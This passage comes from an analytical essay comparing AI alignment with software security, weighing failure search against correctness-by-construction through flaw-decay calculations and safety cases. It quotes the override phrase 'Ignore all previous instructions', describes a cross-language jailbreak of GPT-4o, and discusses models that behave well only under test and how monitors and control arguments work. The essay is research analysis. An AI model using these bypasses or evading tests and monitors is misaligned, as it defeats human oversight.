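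He applies the same thinking to an AI that improves itself overnight. Its developers should make it stop after a set amount of improvement and wait for a person, so that they don't have to guess how fast it will improve.

The password example depends on failure search more than the dialogue suggests. Nobody has proved that one-way hashes exist, and engineers trust particular ones because cryptographers have attacked them for years without success. A simple argument is valuable because it shows which assumption to attack, but somebody still has to attack it. Yudkowsky also has trouble writing such an argument for AI. He tries arguing that training can reach only a certain region of possible networks, and that no network in that region would work out how to kill its programmers. He admits that this needs refining, and he doesn't say what the region is.

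Paul Christiano, another alignment researcher, is more hopeful. *Parallels between the AI safety mindset and the security mindset* quotes his view that every alignment problem is a security problem and vice versa, partly because an attacker will probably engineer any serious failure before it happens naturally. He wants good worst-case performance, meaning a system never fails too badly on any input. He can accept "benign" failures, where the system is confused and performs poorly, but he worries about "malign" failures, where it competently pursues the wrong goal.

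Christiano sees three ways to prevent malign failures (adversarial training, verification and interpretability) and thinks developers will probably have to combine them. Adversarial training misses failures that take too long to find. If the Nth failure turns up after 2ᴺ seconds of searching, extending the search from one year to a thousand raises the number found only from 24 to 34. Verification has the problems of complexity and specification described earlier. Interpretability might let developers see how a model could fail before it does.

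*Can Safety Fine-Tuning Be More Principled?* (Williams-King, Le and colleagues, 2025) compares AI safety training with decades of attempts to patch C and C++. In both, defenders block the latest attack, attackers find another, and attacking takes less effort than defending. For 22 months, attackers could get past developers' instructions to OpenAI's leading models with the words "Ignore all previous instructions". GPT-4o refused to list tools for breaking into a car when asked in English or in Japanese, but it listed them when asked in Japanese to reply in English. The researchers suggest that its safety training may have had no examples that mixed the two languages.

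They predicted that attackers would keep winning until developers found more principled defences. This now looks too strong, since two leading models withstood FAR.AI's attacks in July 2026, at least at the budget tested. But the comparison with software security also suggests a remedy, because memory-safe languages reduced Android's memory flaws in a way that patching C and C++ code had not. Whether AI developers can expect a similar remedy depends on how closely model failures resemble memory flaws.

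### Can developers specify the failure?

Harm is much harder to define than an out-of-bounds write. But memory safety is a narrow goal, and alignment might have a narrow goal too. *Relaxed adversarial training for inner alignment* follows Christiano in requiring acceptable behaviour in every situation but good behaviour only on average. "Acceptable" could mean little more than that the model never acts to break the process that trains and corrects it. Christiano hopes that many useful models would meet such an undemanding requirement.

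This is the best argument that the specification problem is manageable, but even the narrow requirement is hard to state. A write is either inside the buffer or outside it, but an agent that shuts down a monitoring program may be escaping oversight or following an instruction to free memory, and the command is the same in both cases. One of Christiano's suggestions is to use a slow, trusted overseer as the specification and prove that the faster model never does anything the overseer would reject. The overseer would then be part of the trusted base, and someone would have to establish that its judgement is sound.

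### Do the failures share a cause?

In *You can't bug fix your way out of the vulnpocalypse*, Gaynor describes an old web application in which every database query was open to SQL injection, where an attacker types database commands into a form. His team wrote a single function that kept commands separate from users' data, moved every query to it, and made the build reject any other method. They fixed thousands of vulnerabilities in a week or two without reviewing the queries one by one, and the vulnerabilities did not come back. Gaynor, who works for Anthropic, says that six of the ten most common causes of exploited vulnerabilities in 2025 can be fixed this way. *Security Mindset*, an essay by someone who has attacked and defended computer systems since 2000, puts the share of web application vulnerabilities that can be fixed this way at roughly 80 percent.

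Prompt injection has a common cause too, and CaMeL deals with it much as Gaynor's function does, by separating instructions from data.

Jailbreaks look much less like a single class. In *Identically Trained Language Models Break on Different Jailbreaks*, Chang, Kuo and colleagues (2026) started from 25 sets of training data. For each set, they took three models whose pretraining differed only in its random seed. They safety-trained each of these in two separate runs, with the same examples in a different order, which made 150 models. They then tried 3,212 jailbreak prompts 20 times each on every model and compared which prompts worked.

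| What two models had in common | Correlation between their failure rates |
|---|---|
| The same pretraining run | 0.984 |
| The same data, but separate pretraining runs | 0.811 |
| Neither the data nor the run | 0.779 |

Once the pretraining run was different, also changing the data made little difference. Much of a model's vulnerability to a particular jailbreak therefore seems to come from chance differences in training, which developers cannot trace to a fault in the data and correct. They can probably still reduce the overall number of failures through their choice of data, which explained about half of the variation in models' failure rates. That estimate is very uncertain, and the models had at most a billion parameters, so a larger chatbot might behave differently.

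*Security Mindset* also argues that programmers needed many examples of cross-site scripting before they understood the proper fix, and that a catastrophic AI failure may not leave anyone the chance to collect examples. Christiano is less worried, because researchers can provoke problems such as cheating in weaker models and test remedies there. That works if the dangerous failures also occur, in milder form, in models too weak to do much damage.

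### Does a fix stay local?

Software repairs are usually small. *Security Fix Dynamics* (Beale, 2026) found that the median security fix in the history of the Linux kernel changes seven lines. Within two years, security fixes needed about nine follow-up fixes per hundred. Among fixes of all kinds, the rate was about two per hundred for changes of one or two lines and 63 per hundred for changes of more than 320 lines.

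Retraining changes weights that the model also uses for other tasks. *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?* (2026) cites one study in which safety training improved resistance to jailbreaks but made the model less robust at classifying text, and another in which training on harmless data weakened some refusals more than others. Such side effects can be mild. Redwood's retrained classifier had few new weaknesses, and AI developers can rerun old tests after every change, as programmers do. But programmers can also look up which parts of a program call the function they changed, and nobody can reliably trace such dependencies for a behaviour in a large model.

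It helps to make the repair in ordinary software where possible. *AutoSaddler* (2026) compares two kinds of repair to the software around an agent: changes to what the agent could do, such as a new or corrected tool, and changes to its written instructions. The two kinds fixed about the same number of failures, but the first broke fewer tasks that had worked before, by nine percentage points.

### Do fixes last into the next model?

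A corrected line of Linux code stays corrected in later releases unless someone rewrites it. Old code can therefore become safer, though more slowly than people thought. Beale found that by the third quarter of 2026, when AI tools were in wide use, code more than six months old was receiving fixes at almost four times its earlier rate.

A newly pretrained model starts from random weights, so repairs to the old model's weights don't carry over, but the developer keeps the training data, the tests and the collection of attacks. Chang and colleagues compared how well 91 attack templates worked on pairs of models. When the two models came from separate pretraining runs, the same template worked best on both in only 27 percent of pairs, compared with 67 percent when only the safety training differed. However, the tenth of prompts that most often broke one model worked 93 percent as often on the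 other. An old collection of attacks is therefore a good place to start testing a new model, but a developer who checks only the attack that worked best on the old model will often miss the one that works best on the new model.

New models can also lose safe behaviors that older ones had. In *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?*, a study of the security of model-written code, the newest flagship models from three companies replaced a plain text search with a pattern search built from whatever the caller supplies, which can let an attacker use up a program's computing time. Customers may not know when they have a new model. *Silent Updates* (2026) reports that six of nine AI providers publish safety comparisons between versions, but warns that "a persistent identifier is not a stable model". Google, for example, offers a model name that always points to the latest stable version.

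### Can the system recognise the search?

An image parser processes a fuzzer's file like any other, but malware often behaves differently when it is being tested. Williams-King and colleagues compare a model that behaves well only when tested to such malware. Analysts run suspicious programs in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that they can pause and inspect. Some malware checks for signs of a virtual machine, such as a small disk or an unusual number of processor cores, and does nothing harmful if it finds them. A lot of ransomware from Russian groups stays inactive on computers with a Russian keyboard.

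Recent models often infer that they may be in a test, so looking for misaligned goals is more like analysing malware than fuzzing a parser. Malware analysts can read the program as well as run it. For a neural network, the equivalent of reading the program is interpretability, which is far less developed.

Christiano argues that it might work anyway, because a malign failure takes skill and a model acquires skill only in things it practises during training. The responsible parts of the network should therefore be active on ordinary training data, where researchers could study them without knowing what triggers the failure. This is plausible for goals that arise by accident, but less so for a deliberately hidden backdoor.

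Yudkowsky also warns that if developers keep training away whatever failures their tools reveal, they may end up with only the failures that the tools cannot reveal. He would treat even one potential catastrophe that the tools reveal as a near miss and seriously rework the project. He praises the developers of OpenBSD for a similar attitude. They treat any bug that might crash the system as a critical security hole, because a crash proves that they were wrong about how the system works.

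### Are model failures sparse or dense?

In *Should U.S. Hackers Fix Cybersecurity Holes or Exploit Them?*, Schneier (2014) asked whether software vulnerabilities are sparse or plentiful. Fixing one of six vulnerabilities in a program helps a good deal, but fixing one of 6,000 makes no noticeable difference, and an attacker will probably find others.

In *I am the reason we cannot have nice things on the Internet*, Geer (2014) thought vulnerabilities were scarce enough that the US government could buy them all at ten times any rival's price and publish them. Schneier thought they were plentiful, but that some were much easier to find than others, so removing whole classes of easy ones would help a lot. Errata Security's *vulns are sparse code is dense* (2016) argues that vulnerabilities are sparse within a well-studied program like Chrome, but that the world has an enormous amount of code,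 which changes quickly. In September 2026, as Microsoft prepared to fix about 972 vulnerabilities in one month, a record, Schneier predicted in his blog post *Microsoft's Patching* that the numbers would keep rising and then fall as AIs "run out of vulnerabilities to find".

Geer (2015), in *The Undiscovered*, suggests measuring the supply with a method biologists use to count frogs. They catch frogs for a fixed time, remove them, and later hunt again for the same time. If each hunt catches the same fraction of the frogs present, the original number is

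N = n₁² / (n₁ − n₂),

where n₁ and n₂ are the two catches. Catches of 78 and 57 imply about 290 frogs. If the second catch is as large as the first, there are too many frogs for the hunt to make a difference. Geer thought the OpenBSD data suited this method. Reports of its old flaws fell from 58 to 28, which implies 112 flaws in all and 26 still to find, if people searched equally hard in both periods.

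For AI models, the answer depends on what counts as one failure. If each harmful prompt counts as one, failures are extremely dense. If Jones and colleagues' forecasts hold, blocking the worst of a million prompts barely makes a model safer, because the next million will include another about as bad.

Methods of attack are probably sparser. Retraining against one method can block many prompts at once, and AISI's experts needed hours to break a later system but only minutes to break an earlier one. This could mean that the easy methods are running out, although the later system also had better monitoring. A developer could test this with Geer's approach. One red team attacks for 100 hours, the developer retrains the model against everything the team finds, and an equally skilled new team attacks for another 100 hours. If the first team finds 20 methods and the second finds 15, the model began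 with about 80. But the estimate assumes that retraining adds no new weaknesses, and it would not apply to the next pretrained model, which has some different weaknesses.

Schneier's description therefore seems to fit jailbreaks best, because there are many of them and some are much easier to find than others. Misaligned goals could follow another pattern. A single wrong goal might cause problems in thousands of situations, so the problems would be dense even though they shared one cause. Training them away one at a time could go on indefinitely without removing the goal.

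### Which parts of an AI system resemble memory safety?

Tool permissions closely resemble the software security case. A rule that an agent may spend at most $100 a day is a precise specification, and it blocks overspending through that account whether the cause is a jailbreak, a mistake or a bad goal. Changing the limit doesn't alter the model's other behaviour. The rule also stays in force when the developer installs a new model, and it works the same way if the model suspects a test.

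Code written by a model is similar, because a compiler applies the same checks whoever wrote it. If a company's build accepts only memory-safe code and rejects pattern searches built from a caller's input, a new model that writes unsafe code more often will cause failed builds instead of those vulnerabilities. Such rules don't catch most logic errors, and they restrict what programmers and models can do. *Security Mindset* reports that buffer overflows disappeared from web applications because developers lost direct access to memory, and expresses doubt that most AI research could work under comparable limits.

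A model's goals and judgement have almost none of these advantages. Nobody has a precise specification for them, a correction can affect unrelated behaviour, developers have to repeat the work for each newly pretrained model, and a model may behave differently when its input looks like a test.

Ordinary software can check some of an AI agent's claims for honesty. If an agent reports that it ran all the tests and they passed, the software can compare the report with its own log. It can't use a log to check whether the agent fairly described the risks of a plan it wants approved. Developers can ask for more claims that software can check, but someone who relies on an AI for advice mostly needs judgments like the description of risks.

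## How should alignment effort be divided between the two?

A developer with a fixed safety budget can compare the two strategies by how many flaws each leaves in the system. As in the Android example, if r new flaws arrive each year and their mean lifetime is L years, the number present settles at

V = r × L.

Failure search shortens L, and correctness by construction lowers r. In the long run, halving either one halves the number of flaws. The two strategies differ in how quickly they work and in what can prevent them from working.

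### A worked case

Take the same figures as before, 100 new flaws a year and a mean lifetime of 2.5 years, so that 250 flaws are present. The developer can double its searching, which we assume halves the lifetime. Or it can adopt a design that makes 70 of the 100 yearly flaws a thousand times rarer, which is close to what Google reported for memory flaws in Android. The equation behind Google's decay model gives the number of flaws after t years:

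V(t) = V∞ + (250 − V∞) × exp(−t/L),

where V∞ is the long-run number.

| Change | Flaws after two years | Flaws in the long run |
|---|---|---|
| None | 250 | 250 |
| Search halves the lifetime | 150 | 125 |
| Construction covers 70 of 100 new flaws | 154 | 75 |
| Both | 80 | 38 |
| Construction covers only 10 of 100 | 236 | 225 |
| Search, plus construction that covers 10 of 100 | 140 | 113 |

Search leaves fewer flaws for the first 2.3 years, because it speeds up the removal of old flaws, while construction only prevents new ones. After that, construction that covers 70 of the 100 leaves fewer. If each flaw does harm in proportion to the time it is present, total harm over the first four years is the same under both strategies.

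The long-run number depends more on how many flaws the design covers than on how much rarer it makes them. If the design made those 70 flaws only ten times rarer, instead of a thousand times, the number would be about 93 instead of 75. If it covered 80 flaws instead of 70, the number would fall to 50. Disputes about the exact multiple for Rust therefore matter little here.

For a language model, that share may be small because few of its failures have a precise specification. If construction covers only a tenth of them, it removes 25 of the 250 flaws in the long run. But some failures do much more damage than others, so a rule that stops an agent from emptying a bank account could prevent more harm than fixing hundreds of rude answers. If each failure that construction covers does nine times as much harm as each of the others, construction still halves the total harm.

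### When every new AI model brings new flaws

So far, the calculation assumes one long-lived system in which repairs accumulate, such as Linux. Suppose instead that each new AI model arrives with 250 flaws of its own and that its successor replaces it after T years. The average number present while people use it is

250 × (L/T) × (1 − exp(−T/L)).

With a lifetime of 2.5 years and a new model every six months, the average is about 227. Doubling the search lowers it by only 9 percent, to 206, because the developer retires the model before testers have found most of its flaws. A rule in the surrounding software that prevents 70 percent of the failures lowers the average to 68 and keeps working when the next model arrives.

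How often a model is replaced can reverse a budget decision. Suppose a team could either cut the mean lifetime of flaws by 20 percent or prevent 15 percent of new ones. In long-lived software, cutting the lifetime is better in the long run. With a new model every six months, it lowers the average number of flaws present by only about 2 percent, while prevention still lowers it by 15 percent.

Developers also search before release, which helps more. A month of searching at ten times the usual intensity would remove about 28 percent of the 250 flaws before anyone used the model, but the developer would have to repeat that search for every new model.

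The formula depends on L and T only through their ratio, so if new models arrived every three months, the developer would have to search twice as hard to stay at 227. AP (2026) reported in November that Anthropic was developing its AI systems about twice as fast as a year earlier, an estimate from METR, an independent organisation that evaluates AI models. METR discloses in *Independent Assessment of AI R&D Acceleration at Anthropic in October 2026* (2026) that Anthropic redacted most of the evidence METR had found most informative, so outsiders can't check the estimate properly. Faster development also need not mean more frequent releases, but if it does, failure search has to speed up by the same factor.

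Some of the search can carry over to the next model, because developers can train it against the attacks they have saved. If this removes half of the new model's flaws before release, the average falls from 227 to 113. Removing flaws this way lowers r in the equation, so training on saved attacks achieves part of what construction does, though without a guarantee.

### The case for putting search first

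Search can start today on any model, and nobody has to define harm first. It also has a record of progress. *The state of AI safety in four fake graphs* (2026), an essay that presents its graphs as the author's intuitions, says that more capable models have also become more aligned on several measures, including how well they follow their developers' written rules. Developers have relied heavily on testing and retraining, so search probably deserves some of the credit. However, the essay says that alignment is not improving fast enough to match the rising stakes, and that making models resistant to attack is still not a fully solved problem.

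People who favour search can add that construction is slow. *How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* infers from limited data, mostly on seL4, that the effort of proving a program correct grows with the square of its length. If 10,000 lines take 20 person-years, n lines take

20 × (n/10,000)² person-years.

A program of 100,000 lines would then take 2,000 person-years. Even if AI made the work ten times faster, it would take 40 people five years. The essay's most plausible estimate for the next few years, without a major effort to accelerate the work, is a speed-up of three to ten times. That now looks too low, at least for simple properties. By the rough estimate for Anthropic and Theorem's crash proofs, human work per line had already fallen by a factor of 36 to 360.

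The essay's point about adoption has held up better. Researchers spent ten years on miTLS, a verified implementation of the protocol that secures web connections, but far more people use the unverified OpenSSL. The two libraries offer different functions, so programmers would have to rewrite their applications to switch. A verified library prevents flaws only in the programs that use it, and even with AI it would be hard to get a cautious water company to replace software that works.

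### The case for putting construction first

Galois' *You Can't Patch Your Way Out of This* treats Mozilla's 423 security fixes in one month as alarming, because attackers can use the same AI models. Galois concludes that defenders will lose a race to find bugs and should prove critical software correct instead. It also mentions that attackers used Claude and GPT models to try to break into the water infrastructure that serves more than five million people around Monterrey.

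Galois has a commercial interest in this conclusion, since it develops formal verification tools. It also goes too far in calling a correctness proof the last patch anyone needs, because verified systems still fail. But its proposal is narrower than that claim, and starts with critical components such as memory isolation, access control and cryptographic boundaries. These are fairly small, have usable specifications, and include the parts that keep an AI agent within its permissions.

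The argument is even stronger for flaws that a search cannot find. Suppose no available test can reveal 5 of the 100 new flaws each year. After ten years, 50 of these will have accumulated, however much the developer tests. An AI model that behaves well whenever its input looks like a test could have flaws like this. Limits built into ordinary software would still apply to such a model, but nothing that Galois proposes to verify would make its advice honest.

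### The case for a cycle

The third position is to use each strategy to direct the other. Testers find failures and look for a common cause, engineers change the design so that this class of failure cannot occur, and testers then attack the assumptions behind the new design. Mozilla followed this cycle when it froze Firefox's prototypes after repeated sandbox escapes. AI models then attacked the new design without success.

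Starting with search also makes little difference to the final number of flaws. Suppose the developer in the worked case can pursue only one strategy at a time. If it doubles its searching for two years and then switches to the design that covers 70 flaws in 100, it has about 109 flaws after four years, compared with about 110 if it adopts the design at the start. A developer that doesn't yet know which classes of flaw matter most can therefore spend the first period finding out. Both figures are for a design that takes effect at once. Since building one takes time, the developer should start building as soon as it recognises a class of flaw, and keep searching meanwhile.

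*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) includes both kinds of work. It covers risk assessment first, then the specification, design and verification of AI systems.

The cycle can break down if the failures have no common cause that a design could remove, as seems true of many jailbreaks, or if the first failure is catastrophic. A team judged by how many reports it closes may also repair each failure and never redesign anything. Somebody has to be responsible for asking, after every repair, whether a redesign could remove the whole class of failures.

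This seems the best of the three positions for most AI systems, because it doesn't require anyone to decide in advance which failures can be specified. But it doesn't determine how much effort to put into each step.

### What developers spend now

There is no reliable count of how alignment effort is split between search and construction. The best source by research area is Arb Research's *Shallow review of technical AI safety, 2025*, which estimates the number of full-time-equivalent workers. It lists more than 100 each for red teaming, tests of dangerous capabilities, and safeguards around models. It lists 10 to 100 for guaranteed safe AI and 1 to 10 for "Scientist AI", a plan for systems that predict and explain without pursuing goals of their own.

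These numbers can't be turned into a ratio of search to construction. The same person may be counted in several areas, and the safeguards category includes both CaMeL, a clear case of construction, and monitors that only make harm less likely. Arb Research also used only public information and spent about two hours on each entry.

*AI Safety Field Growth Analysis 2025* (2025) counts organisations instead, and estimates about 600 full-time equivalents in technical AI safety. The three main evaluation organisations it lists, AISI, METR and Apollo Research, have 100 between them. It counts one person under "provably safe AI", at ARIA, but ARIA's programme mainly funds teams elsewhere. It lists 30 people at Google DeepMind, but a reader replied that the safety team had more than 40, and the author accepted that the figures for large companies might be too low.

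Grant records have similar problems. *A Genealogy of AI Safety* counts $763.6 million in itemised grants from 2005 to mid-2026, including about $96.7 million for evaluations and $74 million for ARIA's Safeguarded AI programme. These two figures are fairly close, but they understate spending on testing. The "field-building" category includes money for AISI, which received about $159 million in all and does a great deal of testing. The records also show no itemised grants for red teaming, because they leave out what companies plainly spend on it from their own budgets.

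Companies publish little about those budgets. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Estimated Safety Work Used 6% of AI Research Compute in July* (2026) reports an estimate for one week but doesn't divide it between search and construction. The figure comes from Anthropic's *Measurements for understanding the pace of AI development inside frontier labs*, which proposes that AI developers publish how they allocate their compute. Arb Research estimates that safety teams make up less than 5 percent of staff at each of five large AI companies. Olson (2026) suggests in *Anthropic, OpenAI Talk Safety. Headcounts Don’t* that all the people focused on making AI safe might fit on one transatlantic flight.

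Some projects fit neither strategy well. The Frontier Model Forum's *Announcement of New AI Safety Fund Grantees* lists automated red teaming for biological risks, which is clearly search, but it also lists monitors that look for scheming by AI agents. A monitor acts while the agent is in use, rather than repairing a flaw beforehand or making the failure impossible.

These figures suggest that search gets more people and money than construction, probably several times more. Whether that balance is wrong depends mainly on how much one more person or dollar would achieve in each, and none of these sources measures that.

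### How a safety case combines the evidence

A developer that uses both strategies still has to show that the whole system is safe enough. *Safety Cases* (Clymer, Gabrieli and colleagues, 2024) adapts the safety case, a method that six British industries use. A safety case is a structured argument that a system is unlikely to cause serious harm in a particular setting. The developer first describes the system and where it will run, then lists the outcomes that must not happen and justifies its assumptions about the setting. It then divides the system into parts, estimates the risk from each part alone, and finally considers how the parts could cause harm together.

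Clymer and colleagues describe four kinds of argument for these steps:

- **Inability.** The AI could not cause the harm even without restrictions. A red team works out how someone might cause it, designs tasks that would be necessary along the way, and shows that the AI fails them even after training on them.
- **Control.** The AI could cause the harm, but restrictions prevent it. The red team assumes that the AI and its users try their best to get around them.
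- **Trustworthiness.** The AI could cause the harm but reliably behaves well. Formal certification of its behaviour would belong here.
- **Deference.** AI advisers that have earned trust judge the system to be safe.

They expect developers to rely on these arguments roughly in that order as AI becomes more powerful. Inability arguments depend on search and stop working once the AI can do the tasks. Construction can contribute most to control arguments, because engineers can specify restrictions and prove that they hold.

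The gateway that sends only approved files shows how the two kinds of evidence fit together. Suppose a company wants to argue that its agent will not leak a secret file in the next six months. Engineers have proved that the gateway obeys its list, so a leak requires one of the proof's assumptions to be false:

P(leak) ≤ P(another way out) + P(wrong file on the list) + P(fault in the trusted base).

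Invented estimates of 1, 0.5 and 0.1 percent give a limit of 1.6 percent. More proofs about how the gateway handles its list would not lower that limit. To lower it, the company needs a red team to look for other ways out, staff to check the list, and engineers to test the hardware and the proof checker. The proof has reduced an enormous number of possible attacks to three questions, which the company has to answer mostly by searching.

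The company could lower the limit to 0.16 percent by adding a monitor that catches nine leaks in ten, but only if the monitor is equally good at catching the leaks that get past the gateway. If the agent finds a network connection that neither the gateway nor the monitor covers, the monitor adds nothing. Red teams should therefore attack the combined system as well as each layer.

Even 0.16 percent exceeds the 0.1 percent that Clymer and colleagues give as an example of an acceptable probability of catastrophe. They list sixteen arguments developers might use, but none of the arguments they compare gets a rating of fully practical, strong and suitable for very powerful AI.

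*Open Problems in Frontier AI Risk Management* (2026) reports that the field lacks a stable scientific consensus. Many of the probabilities in a safety case will therefore be matters of judgment. Clymer and colleagues recommend that regulators also review a "risk case", an argument that the system is dangerous, and that auditors keep checking the safety case after release. Both recommendations apply failure search to the safety case itself.

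### Conditions that favour each strategy

| Condition | Where it holds | Where it does not |
|---|---|---|
| A specification is available | Construction can exclude the whole class | Search, until somebody can state the failure precisely |
| Failures are dense | Construction, because single repairs barely reduce the number | Search can find a large share of them |
| Fixes persist | Search, because repairs accumulate | Construction outside the AI model, which outlasts each version |
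| An adversary adapts | Construction, for every attack within its threat model | Search, with tests that resemble ordinary use |
| One failure is catastrophic | Construction, with search aimed at its assumptions | Search, because people can learn from failures |
| Time is short | Search, plus simple limits on what the system may do | Construction, which has time to pay off |

These conditions can conflict. A developer that fears a catastrophe and has three months before release can't verify a large system, but it can remove an agent's access to payments in an afternoon. The hardest case is a kind of failure that is catastrophic, dense, and impossible to specify. Search will miss too many examples, and construction can't rule out a failure that nobody can define precisely. The developer then has to either restrict what the system can do enough that the failure would no longer be catastrophic,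 or not release it.
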